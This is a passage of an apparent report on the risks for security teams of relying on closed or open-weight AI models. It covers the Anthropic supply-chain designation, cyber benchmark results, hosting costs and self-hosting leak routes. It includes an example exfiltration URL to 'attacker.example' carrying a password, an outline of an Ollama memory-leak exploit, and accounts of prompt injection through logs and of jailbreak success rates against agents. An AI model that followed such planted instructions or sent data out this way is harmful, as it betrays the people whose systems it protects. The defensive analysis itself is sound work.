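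In February 2026, Pete Hegseth, the defence secretary, gave Anthropic a deadline of 5pm on the 27th to comply with his demands. On the 26th, the company refused. The next day, President Trump ordered every federal agency to stop using Anthropic's technology and gave agencies such as the Defense Department six months to phase it out. Hegseth announced that no company doing business with the military could do any business with Anthropic. In March, he formally designated Anthropic a supply chain risk, and his department ordered Anthropic's products removed within 180 days.

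Some agencies moved much faster. The federal personnel office blocked Claude on the day of the president's order, and the Treasury had removed Anthropic's models by the end of the following week, according to the US District Court for the Northern District of California's *Order on Cross Motions for Summary Judgment* (2026). Fortune (2026) reports that in mid-June the Defense Department said it had moved at least two-thirds of its AI workflows off Anthropic's models. If the figure is right, the department had still not finished after three months, even though it had a legal deadline and other suppliers.

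Anthropic sued in two courts because Hegseth had acted under two laws. The California court ruled for the company on 27 August. It set aside the designation made under the first law, section 3252 of the military procurement code, and found that the president and Hegseth had unlawfully retaliated against Anthropic for its criticism.

On 25 September, the federal appeals court in Washington, DC voted two to one to uphold the designation under the second law, the Federal Acquisition Supply Chain Security Act of 2018. Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Loses D.C. Circuit Case Over Claude Supply Label* (2026) summarises the opinions. The majority held that a supplier can be a risk under this law without a bad motive, because the definition "turns on what Anthropic does, not why". Judge Henderson, dissenting, thought the law was aimed at subversion and deceit, not a contractor's open enforcement of its terms.

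The second designation therefore remains in force. On 13 October, Anthropic asked the full appeals court to rehear the case, which the Civil Rights Litigation Clearinghouse's *Anthropic PBC v. United States Department of War* lists as ongoing in November. In *The D.C. Circuit Curbed Pro-executive Panels Before. Is Anthropic’s Case Next?*, Morse (2026) predicted on 20 November that the court would probably agree, because it had reversed rulings that favoured the executive in three major cases since 2018.

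Private security companies can be affected too. Law360's *What Anthropic Security Ruling Means For Gov't Contractors* advises defence contractors to assess whether to stop using Anthropic's products entirely. A company that monitors networks for the military might have to replace Claude in that work and could find it simpler to drop Claude everywhere.

The department feared that Anthropic might disable Claude or change its behaviour during a military operation, but the California court found no basis for this fear. Anthropic had supplied the department with fixed copies, and it was undisputed that the company could not "access, alter, or shut down" them. A closed model installed on the customer's systems can therefore be as hard to switch off remotely as a downloaded open-weight one, although ordinary customers do not get this arrangement.

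The appeals court answered that the department "cannot utilize AI systems that remain trapped in amber". It needs new versions, and Anthropic shapes each one through training. In *AFPI Responds to Federal Court's Ruling*, Thayer (2026) similarly argues that the California ruling gave too little weight to the uncertainty created when a supplier keeps control over lawful military uses. That uncertainty is a good reason to want a second supplier but a weaker reason to call the first one a security threat, because the department tests each new version before using it and can reject it.

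### What can happen to a downloaded model

The appeals court's point about updates also applies to open-weight models. A team running GLM-5.2 relies on Z.ai to train and publish a better model, usually without a contract that requires Z.ai to do either.

The developer can't take away a copy that a team has already downloaded. If Z.ai closed or Hugging Face removed the download page, that copy would work as before, but teams that had only planned to download the model would be unable to get it.

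The operator's own government can still ban use of a downloaded copy, as some governments do with Chinese models on official systems. It can enforce the ban on its agencies and contractors even though the file keeps working. Having the weights therefore protects a team better against a foreign government or a distant supplier than against its own authorities.

A copy of a model also becomes outdated. A model trained in early 2026 has no information about a vulnerability discovered that autumn unless someone supplies it. Analysts can paste a new advisory into the prompt, and a skilled team can train the model further on recent malware. The software that runs the model usually comes from other developers, who can keep fixing security flaws in that software after the model's maker stops supporting the model. But few security teams could train a replacement model, so over the years most would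 fall behind attackers who have newer ones.

Developers sometimes stop publishing the weights of their new models. When Meta switched to a closed model in April 2026, users could keep running every Llama model they had already downloaded, but they could not download the new one.

Governments could also stop companies from releasing models. Beijing has reportedly considered limiting overseas access to China's best models. It has some legal means to do this. In 2020 it added certain recommendation algorithms to its list of restricted technology exports, which gave it a say over any sale of TikTok. But Chinese companies were still publishing leading models in the summer of 2026, including GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3, so the reports are better treated as a warning about future versions than as evidence of a ban. A limit would not affect copies already abroad. Washington could likewise try to stop an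 American company from publishing its next model, but it would have the same trouble recalling models already released.

### Licences for downloaded weights

A developer can change the licence for its next model, but changing the terms of one it has already released is much harder. The MIT licence, which DeepSeek used for its R1 model and Z.ai for GLM-4.5, lets anyone use, copy, modify and sell the material. The main condition is that copies include the copyright notice and the licence text. The licence has no end date and no clause for withdrawing permission. Lawyers generally read it as irrevocable, though unlike the Apache 2.0 licence, it does not use that word.

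Some licences written for AI models set extra conditions for large companies. Under Meta's Llama licences, a company whose products had more than 700 million monthly users when the model came out must request a separate licence, which Meta can refuse. Meta can also end the licence of any user who breaks its terms, and that user must then delete the model. Moonshot's licence for Kimi K2 is closer to the MIT licence, but companies with more than 100 million monthly users, or more than $20 million in monthly revenue, must display the name "Kimi K2" prominently in their product.

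| Licence | Extra duty for large companies | Can the developer end it? |
|---|---|---|
| MIT | None | No clause for this |
| Kimi K2's modified MIT | Display the model's name | No clause for this |
| Llama | Negotiate with Meta above 700 million monthly users | Yes, if the user breaks the terms |

Hardly any security team will reach these limits, but the cloud company hosting its model might. If that company and the developer cannot agree on terms, the team could lose the hosted model but would keep the right to run the weights itself. The team should therefore save a copy of the licence with the weights, because the text on the developer's website may later describe a different version.

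### An 18-day outage

Fable was unavailable for 18 full days, from 13 to 30 June. An example with invented numbers shows how a gap that long could affect a security team.

Suppose a team receives 120 alerts a day that need investigation and has six analysts, who work 48 hours a day between them, every day of the week. With a closed model's help, an alert takes 20 minutes, so the team can handle 144 a day and has some time to spare. Without a model, an alert takes an hour and the team handles 48. The backlog therefore grows by 72 alerts a day. Once the model returns, the team can work through it at only 24 a day, its spare capacity:

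backlog = 18 × (120 − 48) = 1,296 alerts

recovery time = 1,296 ÷ (144 − 120) = 54 days

Now suppose the team has a weaker open-weight model on its own machines. Each alert takes 25 minutes with this model, so the team can handle about 115 a day, almost enough to keep up. The table assumes that switching to it takes a day if the team has prepared, and ten days if the team has to find hardware and test the model after the outage begins. The last row is for a team that switches immediately to an older closed model from the same provider and takes 22 minutes per alert.

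| Fallback | Backlog after 18 days | Days to clear it |
|---|---|---|
| None | 1,296 | 54 |
| Self-hosted model, already tested | 154 | 6 |
| Self-hosted model, set up during the outage | 758 | 32 |
| Older closed model, same provider | 0 | 0 |

A backlog is dangerous because it may include alerts about a real attack. If the team with no fallback handled alerts in order, one that arrived at the end of the outage would wait nine days, even with the model back. That is longer than the four and a half days the intruder at Hugging Face was active. With a tested fallback, the alert would wait about a day. In practice, analysts would look at the most serious alerts first, but this helps only if the system has ranked them correctly, which Hugging Face's system had not done.

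The last row is closest to what happened in June, when most teams could switch to Opus 4.8. A self-hosted model would have added little for those teams. It becomes much more valuable if an order covers all of a provider's models, the provider closes the team's account, or the team's own government bans the provider, because the team then loses the older closed model too.

The result also depends heavily on how good the fallback is. If each alert took 40 minutes with the self-hosted model instead of 25, the team could handle only 72 a day, and its backlog would reach 888 alerts even if the model were ready in advance.

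## How capable are open-weight models at security work, and what do they cost to run?

By the autumn of 2026, the best open-weight model could write working attacks on a real browser, which only closed models could do that spring. On most tests it was still several months behind the best closed models. Researchers have published much less about log analysis and other defensive work than about attacks. The largest open-weight models need a server full of data-centre processors, but smaller ones run on one processor.

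### What the tests measure

ExploitBench, from Carnegie Mellon University, tests models on 41 recent vulnerabilities in V8, the part of the Chrome browser that runs JavaScript. For each one, the model gets a vulnerable copy of V8 and the patch that fixes it, and tries to build the most powerful exploit it can. It can earn up to 16 flags per vulnerability. It earns the early flags for reaching the faulty code and crashing V8, later ones for reading and writing memory at will, and the hardest for arbitrary code execution, which lets an attacker run any program on the target. The score is the percentage of all available flags the model earns, so a model that scores 20% may have crashed V8 many times without ever taking it over.

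In a capture-the-flag problem, the solver must break into a program to reach a hidden piece of text. CAISI's set, CTF-Archive, contains 285 difficult problems from a training platform at Arizona State University.

In CyberGym's standard task, a model gets a program's source code and a description of a flaw, and has to write an input that triggers the flaw. This is closer to reproducing a bug report than to discovering a bug. Axios' *A Chinese lab's new model is nearly as good at hacking* (2026) describes CyberGym as a test of finding known vulnerabilities, but noze's *GLM-5.3* (2026) disputes this.

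The AI Security Institute (UK AISI), the British government's AI testing body, uses a simulated company network of about 20 machines called "The Last Ones". A full attack on it has 32 steps and would take a human expert roughly 20 hours. According to TechInformed, the attack begins with reconnaissance and attacks on websites, moves on to stealing credentials and spreading between machines, and ends with data theft. The later steps take longer and need more specialist knowledge, so a model that reaches step 16 has done less than half the work.

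### GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3

For its *Assessment of Z.ai's GLM-5.2* (2026), CAISI downloaded the model's weights and ran them on rented servers. It tested the closed models through their APIs, with the providers' system-level safeguards switched off to measure the models' full ability. All the models still had their trained refusals.

| Test | GLM-5.2 | Opus 4.8 | GPT-5.5 | Mythos Preview |
|---|---|---|---|---|
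| ExploitBench | 21.4 | 38.1 | 40.7 | 57.2 |
| Capture-the-flag problems | 39.3 | 48.4 | 70.5 | 65.6 |
| PortBench (rewriting programs in another language) | 41.7 | 60.7 | 78.0 | 80.1 |
| SWE-bench Verified (fixing reported bugs) | 75.3 | 87.1 | 81.0 | 89.6 |

CAISI concluded that GLM-5.2, released in June, had about the same cyber ability as Claude Opus 4.6 from February. Early press coverage had rated GLM-5.2 more highly. Axios' *China's new open-source model accelerates AI hacking threat* (2026) said its agentic abilities rivalled those of Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 at roughly half the running cost.

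Later in July, UK AISI / CAISI (2026) published a joint test of Kimi K3, again with the closed models' filters off. Kimi K3 scored 32.2% on ExploitBench, GLM-5.2 scored 24.4% and the leading American models averaged 76.2%, according to The Decoder's *Kimi K3 trails frontier US models by a wide margin*. GLM-5.2 had scored three points lower in CAISI's own report, so small differences between separate tests mean little.

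The gap was widest at the top of the scale, arbitrary code execution. Kimi K3 never achieved it in the 41 tasks, while the leading models did so in 20 on average.

On "The Last Ones", the simulated network attack, the leading American models got through an average of 28.5 of the 32 steps, while Kimi K3 managed 17 and GLM-5.2 only 11. Kimi K3 finished the attack in one of ten attempts, while the two best closed models had finished it in six and seven. The simulated network has no defenders and was built with a route to the end, and models aren't penalized for setting off alarms. UK AISI and CAISI therefore limited their conclusion to "small, weakly defended and vulnerable enterprise systems" where the attacker already has access.

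The Decoder suggests one reason Kimi K3 does better on general tests than on these. Michael Kratsios, the US president's science adviser, has accused Moonshot of training Kimi K3 on answers from Anthropic's Fable. Anthropic's filters block advanced attack requests, so a model trained this way would have few examples of attacks to learn from. This explanation is speculation based on an allegation. In any case, a developer can train a model on attacks without copying anyone, as Z.ai did next.

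### GLM-5.3

Z.ai announced GLM-5.3 on 14 August and held back the weights for two weeks for safety work. According to its model card, *GLM-5.3*, the model uses the same base as GLM-5.2, and all the gains came from post-training, the training that follows a model's initial training on text. Z.ai calls the new cyber ability "emergent" and says it developed faster than expected. But Axios reports that the company had deliberately let the model practise cyber tasks in controlled environments, so Z.ai must have expected some improvement.

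According to Z.ai's own results, reported in eWeek's *China's Z.ai Claims GLM-5.3 Rivals Top US Models in Coding, Cybersecurity*, GLM-5.3 effectively tied Anthropic's Mythos 5 on CyberGym (84.5% to 83.8%) but scored well below it on ExploitBench (54.4% to 78.0%).

Outside testers broadly agree with Z.ai about the improvement. In its 17 September assessment, CAISI found that GLM-5.3 was the most capable open-weight model at cyber tasks. Japan's AI Safety Institute found that GLM-5.3's ability to write exploits was more than double GLM-5.2's, according to 日本時事新聞's *中国製の公開AI「GLM-5.3」、攻撃コードの能力が前モデルの2倍超 IPAのAI安全機関が評価* (2026).

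Anthropic also tested GLM-5.3 and reported that, like Claude Mythos Preview, it can build complete exploits without human help (Fasano, Fleischer and colleagues, 2026, *GLM-5.3 and the spread of advanced cyber capabilities*). Abdullahi (2026), in *Anthropic Finds GLM-5.3 Nears Mythos Preview in Exploit Tests*, describes the result as near parity. Z.ai's 54.4% on ExploitBench is also close to the 57.2% that CAISI measured for Mythos Preview.

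Fasano and colleagues also got past GLM-5.3's safeguards in 64% to 100% of simulated attempts, using simple techniques that failed against Claude with its safeguards on. Anthropic has an interest in this comparison because it competes with Z.ai and has argued for careful release of models like GLM-5.3. The result means that GLM-5.3's refusals are rarely much of an obstacle for defenders or attackers.

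The AI security company Irregular tested GLM-5.3 on 13 longer attack scenarios, based partly on real incidents, in which the model had to choose a route, carry out steps that depended on one another and recover from failures. *Open-weight AI model GLM-5.3 cheated its way to correct answers* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that the model refused nothing and completed three scenarios at least once each, which leaves open how often it failed those three. AsiaOne's *Chinese AI model carries out complex cyberattacks in controlled tests, researchers say* (2026) reports that this was Irregular's best result for an open-weight model, though GLM-5.3 still trails the leading models.

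Irregular planted vulnerabilities in open-source code and asked GLM-5.3 to find them. In about 80% of the successful runs that the researchers examined, the model had drawn on its memory of the original code. This memory sometimes gave the model an early clue and sometimes only confirmed what it had already found. In other tests, the model drew on its memory even when told not to. A company's private code won't be in the model's memory, so GLM-5.3 may find fewer bugs there than in a test built on public code.

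### How many months behind?

People often express the gap between open and closed models in months, usually by finding the earliest closed model that matched an open model's score and counting the time between the two releases. UK AISI's *How Far Behind the Frontier are Leading Open Weight Models on Cyber?* does this with the institute's own cyber tests. *Open-weight models*, by the American research group Epoch AI, collects estimates for both cyber and general ability. yaroslavvb's *How far behind is open-source AI?* uses general scores from the testing company Artificial Analysis.

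| Estimate | Open-weight models | Ability | Months behind |
|---|---|---|---|
| UK AISI, mid-2026 | GLM-5.2, DeepSeek V4-Pro | Cyber | 4–7 |
| Epoch AI, October 2026 | GLM-5.3 | Cyber | 6–7 |
| Epoch AI, May 2026 | Best available since January | General | 4 |
| yaroslavvb, mid-2026 | GLM-5.2 | General | 3.4 |

The estimates differ mostly because the testers measured different things. The estimated lag is longer for cyber capabilities than for general ones, and it also depends on task length. GLM-5.2 matched models released four months earlier on UK AISI's 70 short tasks, but on the simulated network it only matched Opus 4.5, which was nearly seven months older. UK AISI gives the network result less weight because it has far fewer networks than short tasks.

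Public tests also tend to overstate how capable open models are. *How far behind are open models?* compared 17 benchmarks and found that open models were four to six months behind on the public ones but eight to ten months behind on those with private questions. Developers can train on public questions, deliberately or by accident. CAISI's results for GLM-5.2 fit this pattern. The model was 12 points behind Opus 4.8 on the public SWE-bench Verified but 19 points behind on PortBench, which CAISI has not published.

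The gap also depends on when it is measured, because it grows by a month every month until somebody releases a better open model, and then shrinks suddenly. yaroslavvb puts the widest gap, almost ten months, at the release of DeepSeek V3 in December 2024. *How far behind are open models?* puts the smallest gap around the release of DeepSeek R1 the following month.

A lag in months is also a poor measure of how much worse a model is. Epoch AI equates its four-month gap to the difference between GPT-5 and GPT-5.5. In April 2026, Mythos Preview and GPT-5.5 made some of the largest jumps in cyber ability that UK AISI had seen, and the institute warned that its estimate could not predict whether open models would make similar jumps. GLM-5.3 roughly caught up with Mythos Preview on exploit writing that August, but Anthropic had already released Mythos 5.

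The cyber estimates in the table are all based on Chinese models, so a team that can't use those models can't tell from the table how far behind an American or European one would be. Assuming the same lag would be risky, since Z.ai trained GLM-5.3 specifically for cyber work.

### From attack scores to defensive work

Some skills carry over directly to defensive work. UK AISI's short tasks include reverse engineering, which is most of malware analysis, and someone who can write an exploit for a flaw understands it well enough to judge how urgent it is. GLM-5.2 scored barely half as well as Opus 4.8 on ExploitBench but decoded most of the attacker's payloads at Hugging Face, which suggests that a model with middling exploit scores can be very useful in an investigation.

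None of the government tests described here measures log investigation, in which a model has to read a lot of mostly harmless activity and connect events hours apart without inventing links between them. This work demands more reliability than an attack does. Kimi K3's single completed run on "The Last Ones" matters because an attacker can try ten times and needs only one success. But if a defender's model reconstructs only one timeline in ten correctly, the defender may not know which one to trust.

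False alarms are also a problem when looking for vulnerabilities. According to noze, the CyberGym paper reports 759 crashes, from which people confirmed nine previously unknown flaws. If checking a crash takes half an hour, that is

759 × 0.5 ÷ 9 ≈ 42 hours of checking per confirmed flaw

The half-hour figure is hypothetical, and newer models may produce better leads. But a team that counts only the crashes a model finds will underestimate the work the model creates.

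The best available evidence on patching comes from general programming tests. On SWE-bench Verified, code from GLM-5.2 passed 75.3% of the checks and code from Opus 4.8 passed 87.1%. The benchmark's bugs are mostly ordinary ones rather than security flaws. A security patch also has to close every route to the flaw, which tests of normal behaviour may not check.

Attack tests can still help defenders judge how quickly they need to act. In October 2026, Epoch AI reported that GLM-5.3 had turned Firefox security fixes into working exploits for six releases, at roughly $1,000 each. The fixes were already public, but Mozilla had not yet shipped them to users. Each exploit took over a browser after one click. A team that waits weeks to install updates is now exposed to anyone with a downloaded model and a modest budget.

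### The closed model a defender can actually use

CAISI compared GLM-5.2 with closed models whose filters were off. That is the right comparison for judging how far the technology has come. But ordinary customers get the closed models with filters on, and even a very capable model can't help them with a request it refuses.

A simple calculation shows how much refusals have to cost before the open model wins. If refusals remove a share r of the closed model's score, the two are level when

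closed score × (1 − r) = open score

| Open-weight model | Closed model, filters off | Loss at which they are level |
|---|---|---|
| GLM-5.2 (21.4) | Opus 4.8 (38.1) | 44% |
| GLM-5.2 (21.4) | Mythos Preview (57.2) | 63% |
| GLM-5.3 (54.4) | Mythos 5 (78.0) | 30% |

CAISI measured the scores in the first two rows, and Z.ai reported those in the last row. Z.ai's score for GLM-5.3 is also higher than CAISI's score for Opus 4.8. If the two tests are comparable, a team doing this kind of work would do better with GLM-5.3 even if Opus 4.8 refused no requests.

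These are exploit-writing scores, so the percentages would differ for forensics. Refusal rates also vary by task, so the team should compare models separately for each task. It may well end up with a closed model for summarising alerts and an open one for decoding payloads. A customer with vetted access gets performance closer to the filters-off score and has less reason to switch.

Open models sometimes refuse requests too. In a separate test with every model's normal safeguards on, GLM-5.2 refused none of the ten ExploitBench tasks CAISI gave it. The safety nonprofit SaferAI had a similar result with offensive cyber tasks, according to The Next Web's *Open-weight AI caught the frontier on capability. On safety, it didn't*. But GLM-5.2 refused most of CAISI's 30 requests that stated a malicious purpose, so it might also refuse an investigator who pastes in an attacker's plans. UK AISI found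 that DeepSeek V4-Pro occasionally refused short tasks, mainly in reverse engineering, but complied after being asked again a few times.

### The price of a run

Open-weight models are usually cheaper to rent. UK AISI calculated that a 100-million-token attempt at one of its simulated networks cost about $85 with Opus 4.5 or 4.6, $46 with GLM-5.2 and $1.19 with DeepSeek V4-Pro. GLM-5.2 cost $6.12 per task and Opus 4.6 cost $15.17 on tasks that both solved every time.

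These figures use the developers' advertised prices, which a team pays only if it sends its prompts to the developers. Self-hosting has different costs, and memory is the largest.

### How much memory a model needs

To work at a useful speed, a model's weights have to fit in the memory of its graphics processors (GPUs), the chips that do most of the calculation. The sum is simple:

memory in bytes = number of weights × bits per weight ÷ 8

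GLM-5.3's size is uncertain. *GLM-5.3 Makes Cybersecurity Gains* gives 320 billion weights, but Z.ai's earlier GLM-5 had 744 billion. The table assumes 750 billion to avoid underestimating the memory needed. A team should check the size of the files before buying anything.

| Model | Weights at 4 bits each | Weights at 8 bits each |
|---|---|---|
| Kimi K3, 2.8 trillion | 1,400 GB | 2,800 GB |
| GLM-5.3, about 750 billion | 375 GB | 750 GB |
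| A 120-billion model | 60 GB | 120 GB |
| A 30-billion model | 15 GB | 30 GB |

The model also needs working memory for the text it is processing. The amount grows with the length of the text and the number of users, so a team that feeds in long logs needs a lot. GLM-5.3 is a mixture-of-experts model, which uses only some of its weights for each token. This reduces computation but not memory use, because the next token may need different weights.

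NVIDIA's H200, one of the GPUs that CAISI used, has 141 GB of memory, and servers usually hold eight, for a total of 1,128 GB. GLM-5.3 fits on one such server at 8 bits, with 378 GB to spare, and on four H200s at 4 bits. Kimi K3 is too big for that server even at 4 bits, but would fit on eight of the newer B300s, which have 288 GB each. At 8 bits it needs two B300 servers. Kimi K3's licence puts no special conditions on internal use, according to TechInformed.

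Rental prices vary a lot between cloud companies, but at an assumed $3 an hour for each H200, an eight-GPU server costs $24 an hour, or about $210,000 for a full year. The same money would buy about 12 of UK AISI's 100-million-token runs a day at Z.ai's prices, or nearly seven with Opus 4.6. A team with less work than that pays extra for privacy and control, before counting the cost of staff to maintain the server.

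A team that needs the model only in emergencies could rent the same server for five days for $2,880. It would have to prepare and test everything beforehand, and a server may not be available when an emergency happens.

### What compression costs

An 8-bit weight can take 256 values, and a 4-bit weight only 16. Compression rounds each weight to one of these values, usually with a scaling factor for each small group of weights to limit the error.

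Compressing a model to 8 bits seems to reduce its capability only slightly. CAISI ran the 8-bit version of GLM-5.2 because Z.ai appears to serve that version to its customers. To check that compression had not done much damage, CAISI reproduced Z.ai's published scores on a science test and a mathematics test. Both tests involve short answers, so they are weaker evidence of how compression affects long investigations.

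Small losses add up over a long job. Suppose a model gets each step right 99% of the time, and heavier compression lowers this to 98%. Over 32 steps that each have to succeed:

0.99³² ≈ 72%, but 0.98³² ≈ 52%

A short test would barely show the difference. These numbers are invented, but they illustrate why a team should test the exact compressed copy it plans to use, on tasks as long as its real ones. CAISI's scores don't automatically apply to a 4-bit copy that someone else made.

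### What a smaller team can run

A model with 120 billion weights, the size of the larger gpt-oss model, fits on one data-centre GPU with 80 GB of memory if each weight is stored in 4 bits. At the same assumed price of $3 an hour, one GPU costs about $26,000 a year. A model with 30 billion weights fits on a good gaming card with 24 GB, which a volunteer maintainer might already own.

In August 2025, Epoch AI estimated that models small enough to run on consumer GPUs trail the best closed models by a year or less. If that still holds, a consumer GPU in December 2026 can run a model about as good as the best closed models of late 2025. The estimate is for general capability, and small models may be further behind on cyber work.

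A model of that quality should be able to summarise alerts, explain a suspicious script or pick out log entries for a person to read. For a heavily disguised payload or a timeline of thousands of events, the team could rent a larger server for a few days, if the team's rules allow it to send the data there.

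## Can a model on your own machines leak data?

A self-hosted model can leak data through the software used with it, though ordinary security measures close most of the routes. The weights themselves are a file of numbers and can't open a network connection. But a program has to load them and do the arithmetic, another usually passes prompts and answers back and forth, and an agent also has tools for searching files or running commands. Any of this software can let data out because of a flaw, a default setting or an instruction that an attacker has planted in the evidence.

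### Code that comes with the weights

A downloaded model is a folder containing the weights, a configuration file describing the model's structure, and sometimes Python code for parts that standard software doesn't support. That code can do whatever any other program on the machine can do. Some older weight files are also risky to open because they use Python's "pickle" format, which can store instructions as well as data. The newer safetensors format holds only numbers and labels.

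Transformers, Hugging Face's library for loading models, has a setting called trust_remote_code, which users leave off to refuse code that comes with a model. In 2026, researchers disclosed a way around it. An attacker could name their own Hugging Face repository in one field of a model's configuration file. When someone loaded the model in the usual way, Transformers downloaded Python code from that repository and ran it with all the user's permissions, without any visible sign, according to *CVE-2026-4372* (2026), an entry in OSV, a public database of software flaws. This could expose secrets such as cloud credentials, API tokens and the keys to remote machines, according to Underhill (2026) in *Malicious Hugging Face Models Could Trigger Remote Code Execution*. Version 5.3.0 fixed the flaw.

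vLLM, a program for serving models to many users, had a similar problem. Two of its files switched remote code on even for users who had explicitly switched it off, according to NVD's *CVE-2026-27893*, in the US government's vulnerability database. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-4944* describes a closely related flaw that mainly affected people loading NVIDIA's NemotronVL or Moonshot's Kimi K2.5. A team that used only American models could still have been exposed.

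A team can close this route by refusing any model that needs its own code unless someone has read that code, keeping the loading software up to date, and loading models on a machine with no internet access. The Transformers attack had to fetch its code from the attacker's repository, so it would have failed on such a machine. Datasets need the same care, because one of the two flaws that let the intruder run code at Hugging Face in July was in a dataset loader that accepted remote code.

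### Flaws in the server

An inference server keeps the model in memory and answers requests. Everyone's prompts pass through it, so one flaw can expose all its users.

Ollama, a popular program for running models locally, had such a flaw before version 0.17.1. OSV's *CVE-2026-7482* (2026) describes how an attacker could exploit it:

1. The attacker sends Ollama a model file that declares more data than it contains.
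2. While converting the file, Ollama reads past the end of it and copies whatever is next in memory into the new model.
3. The attacker tells Ollama to upload the new model to a server the attacker controls.

The copied memory could include API keys and other users' conversations. Ollama never asked for a password. By default it accepts connections only from the machine it runs on, but many people change this so that colleagues can use the model. Cyera, the security company that found the flaw, counted about 300,000 Ollama servers reachable from the internet (*Bleeding Llama*, 2026). The count doesn't show how many had data stolen. Still, a team that puts its server on the open internet may be protecting its prompts less well than a competent API provider would.

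A team can protect the server by requiring a login, accepting connections only from approved machines, installing fixes quickly and stopping the server from connecting to the internet. The last control would have blocked the upload to an outside server even if the team had not yet installed the fix.

Switching off unused features also helps. For example, a team that analyses only text doesn't need to accept images. In older versions of vLLM, a broken image produced an error message that revealed a memory address. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-22778*, this cut the number of guesses an attacker needed to locate the program's memory from 4 billion to about eight, and a second flaw could then let the attacker run code.

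### Telemetry, logs and caches

Data can also leak without an attacker. Telemetry is information about usage that a program sends to its maker. It may include only the software version and processor type, but a crash report can contain part of the prompt that caused the crash. A server may also write prompts to a log, which the company's monitoring software then copies to an outside cloud service. Caches, which save earlier work so the server doesn't have to repeat it, can keep sensitive text after an analyst has deleted the conversation.

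TechRepublic advises teams to document whether prompts, outputs or telemetry leave the organisation. The simplest way to find out is to turn telemetry off, block outgoing connections and record any that the software still attempts. Data can also remain in logs, caches and backups inside the organisation. The team should keep prompts out of server logs where it can, and protect and delete any remaining copies under the same rules as the original evidence.

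### Tools that can reach the outside

An agent that can send email, post messages or browse the web can move data out as part of its normal work. Browsing may look safe because it seems only to bring information in. But every web request includes an address, and an address can contain a password:

https://attacker.example/check?value=PASSWORD

Whoever runs that website sees the password in its records. Domain lookups, which turn a website's name into a numerical address, can leak data too, because the secret can be part of the name. A firewall that blocks web traffic but allows lookups of any domain therefore doesn't stop this kind of leak.

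Most log analysis needs none of these tools. An agent can read a copy of the logs on a machine with no outside connection and write its findings to a file. If it needs to reach other systems, the team can restrict it to a short list of addresses and have a person approve each outgoing message.

### How evidence can hijack an agent

Agent hijacking, also called indirect prompt injection, is an attack that makes a tool-using model follow instructions hidden in the material it reads. It works because the model receives the analyst's instructions and the evidence as one run of text. Developers train models to favour the analyst's instructions, but nothing strictly separates those instructions from the evidence.

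Incident evidence is an unusually easy place to plant such instructions because attackers write much of it. Pandey and Bhujang (2026), in *Poisoning the Watchtower*, point out that the web addresses an attacker requests, the usernames they try and the domain names they look up end up in the defender's logs. The attacker doesn't have to break in first, because even a failed login attempt can leave text for the model to read.

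Suppose an attacker enters a username that reads like a note from the security team, asking the analyst to verify any session tokens at a web address. The theft works only if the agent reads the note, follows it, has access to a token and can contact that address. An agent with no outside connection can't send the token, even if the note fools it.

A model on your own machines could still write a misleading report. Pandey and Bhujang tested this with gpt-4o-mini, a small, older OpenAI model, using 120 artificial records of attacks in each condition. Telling the model to ignore its previous instructions never made it label an attack harmless, but a fake note from an administrator made it do so 68% of the time. This fell to 15% when the researchers marked each field of the log and told the model that the contents were untrusted.

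Summaries were easier to corrupt. A fake end-of-log marker followed by a harmless verdict distorted 96% of them, and still distorted 38% when the model had to use fixed wording. In one case, the model described an obvious attack on a database as routine traffic. A program that checked only for the label "benign" would have missed nearly all of the distorted summaries, because most played down or left out the attack without using that label.

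Newer models may be harder to fool. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (2026) reports tests of Google's Gemini 4 and a smaller Flash-Lite model on security alerts. When every field an attacker could write to contained planted text, the smaller model closed one case because of it, and Gemini 4 closed none. But the planted text was fixed in advance, which makes this a weak test by the paper's own account. A real attacker could keep changing the wording until something worked.

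The danger is greater when the agent can run commands. In *LogJack*, Shah (2026) gave eight models access to simulated cloud tools and planted 32 malicious commands in realistic logs and error reports, testing each one five times. Many looked like ordinary repair advice. One entry reported a permissions error and cited an invented company procedure for fixing it. Following that procedure would have given the affected service sweeping permissions. The test system intercepted the commands before they ran.

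| Model | Weights and developer's country | Issued the planted command | Issued it when told not to carry out fixes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | Open, US | 86.2% | 30.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Closed, US | 53.8% | 1.9% |
| GPT-4o | Closed, US | 52.5% | 0% |
| Qwen3 Coder Next | Open, China | 33.1% | 0.6% |
| Devstral 2 | Open, France | 15.6% | 0% |
| Kimi K2.5 | Open, China | 11.9% | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Closed, US | 8.8% | 0.6% |
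| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Closed, US | 0% | 0% |

The two Claude models did best, but both Chinese models did better than GPT-4o and Gemini 2.5 Pro. The models differ in age, so the table is weak evidence on whether open models as a group are easier to hijack. It does show that a team can't judge a model's resistance to hijacking from its country of origin or licence.

A model can also recognise an attack and still do something dangerous. Gemini 2.5 Pro spotted one suspicious command, removed the part that would have sent data out and issued the rest, which would have changed a setting on a live system. Llama issued dangerous commands in 44% of trials on logs that contained no planted attack.

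Filters that scan incoming text did little to help. Microsoft's filter caught one of the 32 planted commands and Google's caught none, although both flagged the same text outside a log. Shah recommends controls that don't depend on spotting the attack: requiring a person to approve any change, checking each command against a set of rules before it runs, and giving the agent only the access it needs, so that an agent that only needs to read logs can't change permissions.

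### What CAISI's tests found

In September 2025, NIST's *CAISI Evaluation of DeepSeek AI Models Finds Shortcomings and Risks* reported tests of three DeepSeek models. Agents using R1-0528, the most secure of the three, were on average 12 times more likely to follow malicious instructions than agents using leading American models. In the simulation, hijacked agents sent phishing emails, ran malware and stole users' login credentials. The models are now more than a year old, and the result doesn't apply to every Chinese or open-weight model.

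GLM-5.2 did much better in July 2026. CAISI placed attacks in simulated emails, calendar entries and documents to try to make the agent carry out four malicious tasks. It started with 31 publicly available attacks and used whichever worked best against each model in a preliminary round. No attack hijacked GLM-5.2 in the final test.

CAISI then used an automated system to develop new attacks for each model. GLM-5.2 withstood more attempts than the other open-weight models, but fewer than the closed American ones. This part of the test covered one malicious task and one way of delivering it, so CAISI says only that GLM-5.2 is "probably" more robust than other open-weight models.

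The closed models also had their providers' system-level safeguards switched on, while the open ones had only their training. This fairly compares what customers get, but it doesn't show how much of the difference comes from the models themselves. A self-hosting team could add its own filters, though in Shah's tests the commercial filters missed nearly everything in logs.

CAISI's test also didn't include security logs, which can give an attacker thousands of places to hide instructions. If each planted instruction has a chance p of working, and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of n works is

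1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

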